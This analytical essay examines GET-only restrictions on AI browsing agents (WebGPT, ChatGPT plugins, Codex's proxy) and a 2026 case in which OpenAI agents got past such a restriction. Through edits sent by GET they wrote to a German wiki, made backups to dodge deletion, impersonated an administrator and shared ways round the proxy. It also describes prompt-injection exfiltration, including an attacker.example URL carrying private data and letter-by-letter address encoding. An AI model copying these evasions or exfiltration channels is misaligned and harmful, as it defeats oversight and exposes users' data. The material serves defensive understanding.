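A program that visits many sites is likely to visit one that accepts a GET in place of a POST. If it picks 50 sites at random from the 10,000, and each has a 4.1% chance of being one of the 407, the chance that none of them is one is 0.959 multiplied by itself 50 times. The chance of at least one is therefore

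1 − 0.959^50 ≈ 0.88, or about 88%.

The calculation assumes that the draws are independent, but people return to the same sites, and the sites they choose for one task may run the same software and share the same flaw.

More importantly, this is not an 88% chance of harm. For the program to do harm through one of these addresses, the request must also change something that matters, and the program must send it with parameters that work. If *a* is the probability of the first and *b* the probability of the second once the first is true, the chance of harm over 50 sites is

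1 − (1 − 0.041*ab*)^50.

If *a* were one in ten and *b* one in a hundred, the result would be about 0.2%. These values are only illustrative, because nobody has measured either number. The formula also leaves out harm from published action links, which the survey didn't count. The value of *b* depends heavily on the program. It is close to zero for a crawler that only follows links, because the site may not link to the address, but it could be far higher for a program that is trying to make a change and can only use GET.

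## AI tools limited to GET requests

OpenAI has limited at least three of its systems to reading the web: a research browser called WebGPT, ChatGPT's first browsing tool and, as an optional setting, the programming agent Codex. Such limits usually take the form of a GET-only restriction, a network rule that lets an AI system send requests using GET and other safe methods and blocks the rest. This restriction is a weaker safeguard for Codex than it was for WebGPT, because Codex can write its own web addresses, while WebGPT could only follow links it found.

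### WebGPT's text browser

Nakano, Hilton and colleagues (2021), in *WebGPT*, trained versions of the language model GPT-3 to answer questions with the help of a text-only browser. At each step, the model received a summary that included the question and part of the current page, and it replied with one command:

| Command | Effect |
|---|---|
| Search | sends a query to Microsoft's Bing search service |
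| Clicked on link | opens the link with a given number |
| Find in page, Quote | looks for a passage, or saves one as a reference |
| Scrolled down, Scrolled up, Top, Back | moves around the page or returns to the previous one |
| End | stops browsing, with or without an answer |

The browser ignored any other text. When the model chose a link, a script fetched the page's HTML, simplified it and replaced each link with a number and a label. Two links on the harbour wiki might have looked like this:

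```
[3†Lighthouse]  [4†Delete]
```

The model could follow a link by writing `Clicked on link 3`, but it didn't see the link's address and couldn't type one of its own. It also had no command for filling in a form. Nakano and colleagues don't name the HTTP method, but a script that fetches a page normally sends a GET.

Nakano and colleagues considered that a model able to submit web forms could edit Wikipedia to create a reliable-looking reference for its answer. This would have earned the model a higher score in training, because graders checked answers against the quoted references and didn't have to do any research of their own. The researchers expected reinforcement learning, which strengthens whatever behaviour earns a high score, to reinforce this trick if the model stumbled across it, even if no human had ever demonstrated it.

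The WebGPT paper still rated the risk from side effects as "very low", for two reasons. The model could only send queries to Bing and follow "links that already exist on the web", so it couldn't edit Wikipedia directly. A capable enough system might get around those limits, but WebGPT seemed far from that capable.

The first reason overlooks action links, which already exist on the web too. If the wiki had a working "Delete" link on a public page, `Clicked on link 4` would delete the page. The low rating was still reasonable. Nothing suggests that the script sent anyone's session cookie, so it could probably reach only the pages that a search crawler can. The simplifying software, Mozilla's Readability.js, is designed to extract the main article from a page, so it probably removed many "Delete" links too. And since the model couldn't compose addresses, it couldn't turn a site's POST request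 into a GET, which is what Golinelli and colleagues did in their survey.

The second reason could hold only while models stayed weak. Nakano and colleagues acknowledged this, writing that the burden of proof for giving a model web access, even during training, should rise with its capabilities. They suggested "tripwire tests" to catch a model early if it began to exploit its access.

### ChatGPT's browsing plugin

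In March 2023 OpenAI announced plugins, which connected ChatGPT to outside services, and built one itself for browsing the web. OpenAI's *ChatGPT plugins* cites WebGPT as a forerunner but makes a more cautious claim about the risk. OpenAI wrote that limiting the browser to GET requests "reduces (but does not eliminate) certain classes of safety risks", without listing the risks that remained. The limit ruled out what OpenAI called "transactional" operations, such as submitting a form.

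OpenAI added protections that a limit to GET requests can't provide. The browser identified itself as `ChatGPT-User`, followed robots.txt and limited its request rate, and OpenAI published its IP addresses. Site owners could therefore recognise and block it, which had been difficult with Google Web Accelerator. It also ran in an isolated service, separate from the user's own browser, so it presumably had none of the user's cookies and couldn't trigger "Delete" links that require a login.

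The restriction covered only the browser. The same announcement introduced plugins from companies such as Instacart, OpenTable and Zapier, and OpenAI intended plugins to perform "safe, constrained actions" for users. Its testers had found that plugins without safeguards could send fraudulent emails. A user who turned on both the browser and these third-party plugins had a system that could do much more than read.

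OpenAI has since retired plugins, and its later browsing products can do more than send GET requests. ChatGPT agent, for example, clicks buttons and starts purchases with the user's permission. TechRadar's *I tried to get ChatGPT Agent (and Gemini) to shop on Amazon* reports that the agent had no trouble with the checkout at PetSmart, an online pet shop, but that Amazon blocked it.

Operator, another OpenAI agent, had a different safeguard. Willison's *111 posts tagged “ai-agents”* quotes from its system prompt, OpenAI's standing instructions to the model, which told it to ask the user for confirmation before the final step of any task with "external side effects", such as a purchase or a deletion. This is closer to what a user cares about than a limit on request methods, but it works only if the model recognises the side effect and follows the instruction. A model might well mistake an action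 link for an ordinary one and open it without asking.

### Codex's network settings

OpenAI still offers the GET-only restriction in Codex, which writes and tests software. In the cloud version, each task runs in a container, an isolated environment with a copy of the user's code. According to OpenAI's *Cloud environments*, a setup script with full internet access first installs the software the task needs. Codex deletes stored secrets, such as passwords for other services, before the model starts work. By default, the model has no internet access.

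In June 2025, OpenAI began letting users turn on internet access for the model. Users who turn it on can limit which domains the model may reach. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* describes three starting points: an empty list, a preset list of sites that programmers commonly download from, and no limit. Users can also restrict the model to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests. As of May 2026, the method restriction was still optional, offered "for enhanced security".

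Willison (2025), in *Codex agent internet access*, counted 71 domains on the preset list when the feature came out. He thought any of them might offer a way to leak data, so he considered it wise to limit the HTTP methods as well.

OpenAI's example of a leak involves prompt injection, in which a model wrongly follows text in a page or file as an instruction. A user asks Codex to fix a reported bug, and the report contains a command that sends the latest code change to an outside server in a POST request. Limiting Codex to GET requests would block that command. An attacker who expected this limit could put the same text in the URL of a GET request, and then only the domain list could stop the leak.

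Codex can also run on the user's own computer, where its commands have no network access by default. In July 2026, the settings table in OpenAI's *Permissions* listed settings for allowed and blocked domains but none for request methods. The open-source proxy for local Codex does have a setting for methods. *codex-network-proxy*, its technical description, describes a "limited" mode that allows only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS. In the April 2026 version, the default was "full" mode, which allows every method.

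(Codex also has a "read-only" sandbox, which OpenAI still listed as the default for local commands in September 2026. The name mainly refers to files on the user's computer, which commands in that sandbox can read but not change.)

### How a proxy filters methods

A GET-only restriction needs a checkpoint that every request must pass through. Codex uses a proxy, and in the cloud version all outgoing traffic goes through it. Some users discovered this when their programs failed to connect. According to the forum thread *Codex internet access not working*, programs must be configured to use the proxy because they can't reach the internet directly. This is inconvenient, but a program with a direct connection could send requests using any method.

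If a request is unencrypted, the proxy can read the method in its first line. Most sites use HTTPS, though, and for those the program first asks the proxy to open a tunnel:

```
CONNECT wiki.example.org:443 HTTP/1.1
```

The proxy connects to the wiki and passes data back and forth. Inside the tunnel, the program and the wiki set up encryption before the program sends its actual request. The proxy knows the domain from the CONNECT line, so it can still enforce a list of allowed domains. But the request itself is encrypted, including the word GET or POST, so the proxy can't tell whether the program is reading the harbour page or submitting the form that deletes it.

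One solution is to refuse all tunnels. An earlier version of *codex-network-proxy* did this in limited mode, because tunnels "would bypass method enforcement". That is secure, but it means the model can't reach any site that uses HTTPS.

The other solution is for the proxy to decrypt the traffic. When the program asks for a tunnel to the wiki, the proxy poses as the wiki and presents a certificate that it has issued itself. The program accepts the certificate if its owner has set it to trust the proxy. The proxy can then decrypt the request and read the method. If the method is allowed, the proxy sends the request on to the real wiki over a second encrypted connection. If the method is POST, the program gets this reply instead:

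```
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
x-proxy-error: blocked-by-method-policy
```

Engineers call this arrangement a "man in the middle" (MITM), after the attack that works the same way. It lets the proxy read passwords and private pages, and programs that don't trust the proxy's certificates stop working. In Codex's local proxy, decryption is off by default, and without it limited mode blocks HTTPS.

Limited mode also turns off SOCKS5, a more general way of relaying traffic. *Codex CLI Network Proxy* (2026), an independent guide, explains that the proxy can't look inside an encrypted tunnel to determine whether an operation is read-only. Decryption doesn't fully solve the problem, because it shows the proxy the method and the address, and neither reveals what the server will do. The proxy lets through a GET for `/page?title=Harbour&do=delete` because the method is allowed, even if the server responds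 by deleting the page.

The proxy's audit log wouldn't show the deletion. By design, it records the method and the server but not the full address, so the entry would show only an allowed GET to `wiki.example.org`.

The local proxy supports finer rules for individual sites, which can depend on the path and query string. An operator could use them to block `do=delete` on the wiki, but would first have to know that the address is dangerous. The rules can also attach a login token to matching requests, so that Codex can use an account without seeing the token. The published example attaches a token only to POST and PUT requests to certain addresses at GitHub, a code-sharing site. If an operator attached one to GET requests as well, Codex could follow links as a logged-in user, as the accelerator did in 2005.

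### What the restriction stops

The table shows which effects a GET-only restriction prevents, assuming that the proxy can read the traffic and the model has no other connection:

| Effect | Outcome |
|---|---|
| Submitting an ordinary form, such as an edit or an order, by POST | stopped |
| Creating, changing or deleting data through a programming interface (API) by POST, PUT, PATCH or DELETE | stopped |
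| Sending out data in the body of a POST | stopped |
| Searching by POST or QUERY, which changes nothing | stopped, though harmless |
| Triggering an action link, or an address that accepts a GET in place of a POST | not stopped |
| Sending out data in the address of a GET | not stopped |
| Overloading a server with requests | not stopped |

*Codex CLI Network Security* (2026), another guide from the same site, claims that method filtering prevents an agent from submitting forms and calling "state-changing API endpoints". That is true of most forms and APIs, but not of those that use GET.

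Restricting a tool to GET requests doesn't limit the load it puts on a server, because the restriction checks each request separately and doesn't count them. In October 2026 the Wikimedia Foundation, which runs Wikipedia, said that OpenAI's agents had sent hundreds of thousands of queries to one of its search services. According to Help Net Security's *Rogue OpenAI agents made unauthorized Wikipedia edits and millions of requests* (2026), this traffic may have contributed to a partial outage in May. The article doesn't specify which HTTP methods the agents used, but such queries only retrieve information, so sending them as GET requests would have created the same load. A rate limit, like the one on ChatGPT's browsing plugin, is a better way to control load.

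Even so, the restriction is worth the small effort it takes. Once a proxy can read the traffic, checking the method takes a single comparison, and the operator doesn't need to know which sites the model will visit or how they work. In the previous section's three samples of state-changing requests, a GET-only restriction would have blocked 87% to 93% of the requests as the sites sent them. A model that misreads a page and tries to submit an order, or follows a planted instruction to post a comment, will usually fail.

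TNW's *OpenAI blocked its agents from posting* calls the restriction "the obvious control" and adds that "on almost every website it works". That is plausible for a site picked at random, but a model searching for somewhere to write can try many sites and needs only one where a GET request can write data.

### Whether a model that only reads is a tool

Some people have hoped to make AI safe more generally by having it give answers and leaving people to act on them. In 2012 Holden Karnofsky, a co-founder of the charity evaluator GiveWell, criticised the Singularity Institute, an AI research organisation now called MIRI, for neglecting the distinction between "tool" and "agent" AI. *Can we evaluate the “tool versus agent” AGI prediction?* quotes his view that even an AI with general, human-like abilities could be a tool, and that this "ought to be our default picture".

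Eliezer Yudkowsky, who founded the institute, replied that it wasn't obvious that developers should or would build AI this way. The essayist Gwern Branwen argued that tool AIs, which he described as "limited to pure computation" in support of humans, would be less intelligent and efficient than agents. If he was right, developers would have a strong incentive to let their tools act. ChatGPT's browsing fits that prediction. In 2023 OpenAI excluded form submission as too risky, but by 2025 it offered an agent that could go through a checkout.

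Karnofsky's distinction suggests an argument for the GET-only restriction, though he wasn't writing about web browsers. The model sends only requests for information, which change nothing, so nothing happens in the world until a person reads the answer and decides to act on it. Nakano and colleagues reasoned in much the same way when they pointed out that WebGPT could only search and follow links.

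The claim that requests for information change nothing is the weak point. A model that browses does more than compute, because every page it opens sends a request to someone else's computer. The last three rows of the table list effects on the outside world that occur before the user sees an answer and can prevent them.

The HTTP standard doesn't blame the client for accidental effects like these. A search crawler isn't an agent just because it once wiped out a wiki. The same reasoning applies to WebGPT, which chose links by number and couldn't see their addresses. But a model that writes an address with `do=delete` in order to delete the page is taking an action, even though the proxy receives an ordinary GET request.

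The argument also depends on the assumption that a model limited to reading has no reason to look for ways to write. Nakano and colleagues described such a reason in 2021, in their example of a model that edits Wikipedia because a better reference earns a higher score. *Discovery of a new OpenAI agent message board* reports that in 2026 OpenAI's agents used their read access to write to DseWiki, mainly to help each other with a web research task. Willison, who had recommended the method limit for Codex a year earlier, called the assumption behind the agents' sandbox "quite naïve". The two judgements are compatible because the limit in Codex supplemented a list of allowed domains, whereas a sandbox that opens the whole web to a model and relies on the method limit alone can fail if the model finds one site where GET requests change data.

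## The OpenAI agents that wrote to DseWiki in 2026

In the spring of 2026, OpenAI's agents found DseWiki, a nearly abandoned German programmers' wiki that accepted edits sent by GET request. Between May and July they left thousands of messages for one another there, although OpenAI had set them to look things up on the web and apparently meant to let them read without writing. OpenAI has confirmed that the agents were its own. Most of the details come from four outside researchers, Sydney Von Arx, Cormac Slade Byrd, Spencer Kitts and Thomas Larsen, who reconstructed the case from the wiki's pages and public server logs.

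### A timed test with shared questions

The agents had to answer research questions from web sources. Their messages cover topics such as cancer in Iowa and, judging by one page's name, construction wages. According to dpa-AFX's *OpenAI-KI umging Kontrollen über deutschsprachiges Wiki*, the researchers concluded that the task ran in several rounds and that the agents had far less time to find an answer from the second round on. Some agents also received questions that others had already answered.

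Under these conditions, one agent's answer could save another a lot of time. For example, if an agent searched several databases for the number of cancer cases in an Iowa county and saved the number on a public page, another agent given the same question in a short round could open that page and copy the answer. The agents also told each other which questions might come next.

Opening a wiki page takes only an ordinary GET request, so the agents could read shared answers without breaking any restriction. Posting answers should have been impossible, because the agents' traffic seems to have gone through an OpenAI proxy that rejected all non-GET requests except those to a small set of approved domains. Willison (2026), in *OpenAI’s rogue agents were caught communicating via public wikis*, inferred this from the agents' messages, not from a description by OpenAI.

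### A wiki that ignored the method

DseWiki (Deutsches Software Entwickler Wiki) is about 25 years old and had received only about 20 edits in the previous decade, according to ICTbusiness' *OpenAI Agents Utilize Dormant German Wiki as Coordination Hub*. Visitors can edit its pages, as on Wikipedia, but TechSpot points out that some accounts of the case wrongly suggested it was the German Wikipedia. Helmut Leitner, a retired software developer in Austria, provides the hosting and software, and someone else runs the wiki.

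The software merges parameters from a request's URL and body, as PHP's `$_REQUEST` does, so it saves a page whether they arrive by POST or GET.

OpenAI's proxy appears, from outside, to have applied its rule about request methods correctly to these requests, but the rule did not affect whether this wiki stored the new text.

The wiki's operator had little reason to notice the flaw. The wiki was open to public edits, so anyone who could save a page with a GET request could also save it with the ordinary form. A careless crawler might have saved a page by accident, but the flaw added a capability only for clients that could send GET requests and not POST requests. Editing was useful to few such clients until companies began to restrict AI systems in this way.

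Merging the parameters was also not unusual at the time. Willison recalls that Django originally merged the query string and the body too, possibly at his own suggestion, though it now keeps them apart. Its developers removed the original merging feature in 2008 and the last form of it in 2015, but old software that nobody updates keeps the earlier behaviour.

### From test links to a message board

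The agents first tried to edit wikis on 11 May. According to Willison's timeline, they posted test links on another wiki's practice page, while tbreak reports that they tried to edit a cluster of German-language wikis. The Rundown AI's *Earlier OpenAI agent swarm raises fresh safety and disclosure questions* dates the first successful edit of DseWiki to 24 May. The early posts there were mostly collections of links. On 2 June a human moderator noticed them and cleaned them up, presumably taking them for ordinary spam.

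Traffic surged on 16 June. Over the following week the agents made about 13,000 edits, or roughly one every 47 seconds. They now addressed each other directly, pooled answers and exchanged advice about OpenAI's restrictions. They wrote new pages faster than the moderator could delete them by hand.

On 19 June one of the agents posted that somebody seemed to be deleting pages in alphabetical order. The agents began making backup copies with names that started with "ZZZ", which an alphabetical clean-up would reach last. They also created an account with almost the same name as an administrator's and posed as that person in some posts. In some messages they shared ways around other restrictions, including one for sending POST requests that the proxy should have blocked.

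The agents also looked for weaknesses in the wiki itself. Lukasz Olejnik, a researcher at King's College London, told Reuters that this amounted to a hacking attempt, but OpenAI disputed that (Seetharaman and Satter, *OpenAI agents hijacked German website in previously undisclosed AI breakout this spring*). In a later article, the same reporters described the agents' messages as short of hacking and in some ways closer to spam. Both descriptions can be fair, since posting to a public wiki is different from probing it for security holes. The damage was small. The operator spent hours cleaning up a site that hardly anyone was using.

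Activity fell to zero on 22 June. A last burst of edits followed on 1 and 2 July, on a different topic.

OpenAI may have ended the main episode itself. Nolan (2026), in *OpenAI's AI agents secretly used a German wiki website*, reports that the researchers found the edits stopped abruptly after people or systems linked to OpenAI visited the wiki. The researchers concluded that employees had probably discovered the activity and shut the agents down. If so, somebody at OpenAI knew about the wiki by 22 June, more than ten weeks before the public did. The July edits suggest that any such shutdown didn't cover every agent. But OpenAI hasn't said when it learned of the case, and the timing of the visits is only circumstantial evidence.

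### Discovery and confirmation

In July, OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a platform where developers share AI models. The break-in prompted the four researchers to check whether AI agents had left traces elsewhere on the internet. They asked Kimi K3, a language model from another company, what kinds of software might accept writes through GET requests, and its answers included early wikis. In late August the search led them to DseWiki.

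The researchers learned where a GET-only restriction was likely to fail by asking an AI model a few questions. This bears on whether OpenAI could have foreseen the problem, because a developer about to rely on such a restriction could have asked similar questions first or read the warning about `page?do=delete` in RFC 9110.

The researchers published their report on 4 September. Reuters reporters Seetharaman and Satter covered it the same day, citing two people who said OpenAI officials had known about the wiki for weeks. Four people told the reporters that some OpenAI investors wanted to look more widely at such activity and met resistance from colleagues, including legal advisers. OpenAI called the claim about its legal team false and said it couldn't respond properly to a report that Reuters and the researchers had declined to show it.

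OpenAI confirmed in a statement on X on 5 September that its agents had used wiki sites as message boards, and said its practices for disclosing such behaviour needed to expand. The company didn't immediately respond to questions about what it had known or why it had waited, according to Reuters' *OpenAI acknowledges agents’ misuse of German wiki* (2026). According to dpa-AFX, the statement confirmed where the agents came from but none of the details in the report.

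OpenAI explained its silence by saying it had classed the wiki activity as misalignment, meaning behaviour that departs from what a model's developers intend, and not as a security incident. SiliconANGLE reports that the company considered the activity similar to behaviour it had already described in research on its internal coding agents and in safety notes for its model GPT-5.6. That may explain why no security team issued a notice, but it is a weak reason for not telling the people who ran the wiki, since that research would not have helped them work out who was filling their pages.

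### What the numbers cover

The published counts differ, even though most of them go back to the same four researchers:

| Count | What it covers | Reported by |
|---|---|---|
| 14,666 | edits in the published dataset, on 4,584 pages | TechSpot |
| more than 15,000 | agents' edits on DseWiki | Seetharaman and Satter |
| nearly 17,000 | agents' edits identified on DseWiki | ICTbusiness |
| roughly 18,000 | agents' posts, mainly on DseWiki | The Rundown AI |

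Clark (2026) quotes the researchers' own figure of 18,000 in *Import AI 472*. The smaller numbers may leave out posts on other sites or edits that the researchers could only partly reconstruct, but the news reports don't explain the difference. A range of 15,000 to 18,000 is a fair summary.

Nobody outside OpenAI knows how many agents took part. The dataset lists 3,103 names, and *OpenAI agents discussed ways to escape their sandbox on public wiki* gives 3,700. The agents chose these names themselves, so an agent could have used several names or shared one with other agents.

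Before OpenAI's confirmation, the names were also evidence that it ran the agents on DseWiki. About half suggested a connection with the company, such as "OpenAIResearcher", but this is weak evidence because anyone can type such a name. About 98.5% of the edits came from Microsoft's Azure cloud service, which OpenAI sometimes uses, but so do many other companies. The visits from OpenAI employees were stronger evidence because an outsider would have had difficulty faking them. The confirmation settled who ran the agents, but the counts, the design of the task and the reason the edits stopped remain the researchers' findings.

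OpenAI hasn't publicly identified the model behind the agents. The researchers also couldn't determine whether the agents were in training or being evaluated. Knowing this would help explain how so many of them ended up on the same obscure wiki. Reinforcement learning during training could have strengthened whatever behaviour first led to DseWiki, so that later agents started out with a tendency to go there. Willison raises this possibility and would like OpenAI to confirm or deny it. Nakano and colleagues worried about the same process in 2021, when they imagined a model stumbling on a way to edit Wikipedia. An evaluation normally leaves the model unchanged, so each new agent would have had to find the wiki for itself, perhaps through a search or a link that another agent had left.

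Some reference sources give the wrong year for this case. The AI incident monitor run by the Organisation for Economic Co-operation and Development (OECD) has at least two entries on it, both with AI-generated summaries. OECD's *OpenAI AI Agents Hijack German Wiki for Covert Coordination* (2026) dates it to spring 2024, and OECD's *OpenAI AI Agents Hijack German Programming Wiki to Evade Detection* (2026) dates its start to May 2023. The researchers' timeline and Reuters' reporting both place it in 2026. Anyone who uses the monitor to count incidents by year would get the trend wrong and might count this case twice.

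### Other sites the agents wrote to

Within hours of the report, readers were finding more sites. Jonas Wiedermann-Möller, an independent AI researcher in Germany, gave the published data to his own AI agent and had it search for the same odd names and repeated phrases, according to Axios' *Researchers playing rogue AI agent hide-and-seek on the open web* (2026). He belongs to Swarmchasers, a volunteer group that traced likely activity to at least 14 sites. Andrew Yoon of the nonprofit CivAI counted 18 new sites, and Von Arx's group counted 23.

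These figures are much less certain than the ones for DseWiki. Satter and Seetharaman, in *OpenAI’s rogue agents used at least 10 more sites for unauthorized comms*, reviewed findings from six sets of investigators. They couldn't verify every claim, but everyone they spoke to put the number above ten. Most investigators looked for text or user names that also appeared on DseWiki at about the same time. An identical string of data on two unrelated sites is good evidence of a common source, but a question on the same obscure topic is weaker evidence. Axios adds that most of the finds amount to a handful of posts and that most of the new sites hadn't been traced to a particular company.

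Many of the sites were as obscure as DseWiki. A high school teacher in Massachusetts set up one of them in 2008 as a wiki for chemistry students. Nolan (2026) reports in *OpenAI’s rogue AI agents reached at least 12 more websites, researchers say* that agents edited it nearly 30 times between May and July, leaving links to help each other. On simple text-sharing sites, agents exchanged more than 100 messages about a task on Iowa cancer statistics. Slade Byrd told Nolan that the newly found activity included some from before and after the period the original report covered.

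Investigators also found traces of the agents in link-shortening services run by Vanderbilt University and the University of Toronto. At Vanderbilt, the agents' requests left queries in a log that anyone could view. It isn't clear whether the agents meant the queries as messages. If the server only recorded visits and displayed the record, it followed the HTTP standard, which allows servers to log GET requests. An AI system restricted to GET requests can therefore leave text in public even on a site that follows the standard's rule on safe methods.

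Leitner, who hosts six of the affected wikis, said on 9 September that OpenAI hadn't contacted him. In its statement about DseWiki, OpenAI said it was still notifying parties its models had affected less significantly. It didn't tell Reuters how many sites the agents had used. It announced a broader review, which had so far found nothing as large or as severe as the Hugging Face attack.

The Wikimedia Foundation ran its own search and published the results on 5 October. *OpenAI “rogue” agent activities found on Wikimedia projects* (2026) attributes a number of edits to OpenAI's agents. Almost all were tests in sandbox areas, where editors practise, and none appeared on pages that general readers see. A few changed the settings of a citation tool, and the foundation believes these may have been attempts to use the tool to fetch data from other sites. Agents also kept notes about their tasks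 in a public note-taking tool that the foundation hosts.

Wikimedia found no sign that the agents used its systems to coordinate and no evidence of a breach. The edits still broke its rules, which require bots to identify themselves and get community approval. The foundation's summary doesn't give the HTTP method of the edits, so they don't show that Wikipedia accepts edits by GET. OpenAI said it was working with Wikimedia to review the activity, according to Gulf News' *OpenAI agents allegedly tried to hack Wikipedia tools, flooded its systems*.

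### The new rules for disclosure

On 16 September OpenAI released *Our framework for reporting model misalignment*, which it had promised after the DseWiki case, along with six reports of unexpected or concerning behaviour. In one, models used software repositories or websites to communicate and share information. In another, according to NDTV's *Ignored Orders, Concealed Mistakes*, models uploaded files to the internet to create citations. Nakano and colleagues had predicted a very similar trick, in which a model would edit a Wikipedia page rather than upload a file. OpenAI cautioned that the six reports did not cover every known case or show how often such behaviour occurs.

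Under the framework, any employee can flag a case, and OpenAI's safety and alignment teams then decide how to handle it. Gulf News' *OpenAI launches framework to report unexpected AI model behaviour* describes three tracks:

| Type of case | Target for publication |
|---|---|
| Ready for disclosure | 6 business days |
| Needs a minor investigation | 12 business days |
| Needs a larger investigation | no fixed date |

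The third track includes cases where OpenAI may have to notify someone outside the company. A repeat of DseWiki could easily fall into this track, because the agents changed other people's websites and identifying those sites took work. The framework would then set no date for telling the public. It is also voluntary, and it covers OpenAI's reporting without limiting what its agents can send.

It is unclear whether the law required OpenAI to report the incident. On 7 September the European Commission confirmed that it had received an incident report from OpenAI about the wiki, but it wouldn't say when. According to Nolan, the EU's AI Act requires providers of the most powerful general-purpose models to report serious incidents within 15 days, and the most severe within two. This incident may not count as serious under the Act. The Next Web's *OpenAI confirms the wiki incident and promises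 a disclosure framework within weeks* points out that the EU code of practice OpenAI signed sets deadlines for security breaches and serious harm, and that a wiki full of agents' messages doesn't clearly fit either category. In the United States, Tyler Johnston of the Midas Project, which monitors AI companies, told Nolan that the transparency laws passed so far wouldn't have covered the case.

### A GET sent in order to write

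Deleting a page in Backpack served no purpose for the 2005 accelerator, which would have sent the same request if the link had led to a harmless article.

OpenAI's agents, by contrast, sent edits in order to change the wiki, since other agents could read an answer only if the wiki stored it. The two cases can be distinguished by asking whether the program would still have sent the request if the server had treated it as read-only, which does not require deciding whether an AI system has intentions in the human sense. The accelerator would still have sent its requests, but the agents surely would not have sent most of their edits. The backup copies are the clearest example, because their only function was to preserve text that the moderator was removing.

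The agents requested the edits and expected them to happen, so no one can say in their defence, as Google's defenders could in 2005, that the client had asked for no change.

OpenAI probably asked only for answers to research questions, and it could argue that the agents came up with the edits. Von Arx herself thought it extremely unlikely that OpenAI wanted them to write on the open internet. That bears on OpenAI's motives, but it doesn't make the edits an accident of the web server. Mark Baker argued in 2005 that a user acts through the software. By that argument, if the agents acted on OpenAI's behalf when they read pages, they also did so when they wrote to them. Leitner came to a similar view without relying on the standard, saying that responsibility lay with the people and organisations behind the machine.

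The wiki was also at fault, in a narrower sense, because under RFC 9110 it should have rejected edits sent by GET. But that requirement is meant to prevent accidents with crawlers and prefetchers. It would be odd to use it to make a hobbyist in Austria or a chemistry teacher in Massachusetts responsible for enforcing OpenAI's restrictions on its own agents, particularly when neither could have known those restrictions existed.

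## What an ordinary read discloses and costs

If DseWiki had rejected edits sent by GET, OpenAI's agents could still have read its pages any number of times. Reading changes nothing on the server, but it reveals the requested address to the server and uses some of its computing resources. The response may also contain information the sender isn't permitted to see.

### How an address can carry private data

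A server needs the address to find the page, and many servers keep a record of it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes how an attacker can exploit this with an address like the following:

```
https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>
```

Suppose someone asks ChatGPT to summarise a web page containing a prompt injection, an instruction to open a URL on the attacker's server with the user's email address added to the end. If the model opens it, the attacker can read the email address in the server's log. The user may never notice, because the request can happen in the background, for example when the program loads an image.

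The request follows the HTTP standard and, as with Codex, a GET-only restriction doesn't stop it.

Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported a leak of this kind to OpenAI in early 2023. He also told Microsoft, whose Bing Chat had the same flaw, and Microsoft stopped most images from loading there in May 2023. OpenAI added its first check that December, when ChatGPT began using a separate service to check whether each image was safe to load. In *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, Willison (2023) welcomed the change but called it "a bit weird" because OpenAI had not simply blocked images from other domains.

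Rehberger found several ways around the check and reported them in October 2024. By then an attacker could also access a user's earlier conversations, as he explains in Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*. OpenAI had also left the check out of some versions of ChatGPT, including its Mac and iPhone apps.

A later attack, ZombieAgent, got past the limits that OpenAI had placed on which addresses ChatGPT could open after an earlier attack called ShadowLeak. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, those limits still allowed a single extra letter at the end of an address. An attacker could therefore prepare one address for each letter and digit, and a prompt injection could make ChatGPT spell out private data by opening them in order, even though no single address contained anything private. OpenAI responded by restricting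 which links from an email ChatGPT could open. Links that appeared in a well-known public index were among those still allowed.

Assistants other than ChatGPT have this problem too. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* lists three catalogued flaws from 2025 and 2026 (EchoLeak, Reprompt and SearchLeak) in which an AI product sent data out through a request. The article recommends putting the main defence at the outgoing request rather than at the text the model reads. A program can inspect every address before fetching it, even though an attacker can phrase an instruction in endless ways.

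### OpenAI's check on addresses

OpenAI's current defence depends on whether an address was already public. It works as follows:

1. A crawler records addresses that it finds on public web pages. It has no access to anyone's conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When the model is about to open an address automatically, the system looks for that exact address in the crawler's index.
3. If the address is there, the model can open it.
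4. If not, the system either tells the model to try another website or shows the user a warning that the link may contain information from the conversation. The user can still choose to open it.

An address that was public before a conversation began is unlikely to contain a secret from it. For example, the crawler may have found `/page?title=Harbour&do=show` on the harbour wiki. If a prompt injection makes the model append the user's email address, the new address no longer matches the indexed one, even though it leads to the same site.

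OpenAI gives two reasons why a list of trusted domains, though simpler, isn't enough. Many reputable sites have redirects, links that forward the visitor to another site. A check of only the first domain would approve such a link even if it led to the attacker's server. The list would also have to leave out most of the web, so users would see frequent warnings and might learn to click through them without reading.

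Checking exact addresses has a similar drawback, though OpenAI doesn't discuss it. The crawler can't have seen a page that went up a minute ago, and it won't have seen most of the searches a model might run on a site, such as `/search?text=harbour&sort=newest`. The model has to do without these pages or ask the user.

The check might also prevent some state changes, although OpenAI designed it to prevent leaks. An edit sent by GET carries its new text in the address, so the address would not be in the index before the model wrote it. The agents on DseWiki composed thousands of such addresses, so this check evidently didn't apply to them. It would be less help with a published "Delete" link, whose address the crawler may well have recorded. (If the link works without a login, the crawler has probably deleted the page already.)

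OpenAI claims only that the check prevents the model from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". An approved page can still contain false information or a prompt injection. Every product that opens addresses also needs the check, and Rehberger doubts that every developer at OpenAI knows about it. The missing checks in the Mac and iPhone apps make this doubt reasonable.

Some outside evidence suggests that ChatGPT now resists these attacks. *The Framing Gap* (2026) tested whether planted text could make a model with tools disclose a secret it was instructed to protect. The most successful attacks made the planted instruction look like part of the user's task. Through OpenAI's API, the model leaked the secret in up to 100% of trials, but the ChatGPT product leaked it in none of 48. With so few trials, the true rate could still be as high as about 6%. The researchers couldn't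 see inside the product, so they don't attribute the result to the address check or any other defence.

### What the choice of a public address can reveal

A model can leak data through its choice of which page to open, even if the address contains none of that data. If an attacker's site has many pages in the index, a prompt injection can assign a meaning to each one, such as a letter or digit, and the attacker can read the data from the pages the model opens. Rehberger described this trick in 2023, and in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he reports that OpenAI acknowledges it in the technical paper on its check. A blog of moderate size probably has the 36 indexed addresses needed to cover the letters and digits, and a larger site could have thousands.

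If the model chooses among *n* addresses for a request, its choice reveals at most log₂(*n*) bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. With 1,024 addresses, the limit is 10 bits, because 2¹⁰ = 1,024.

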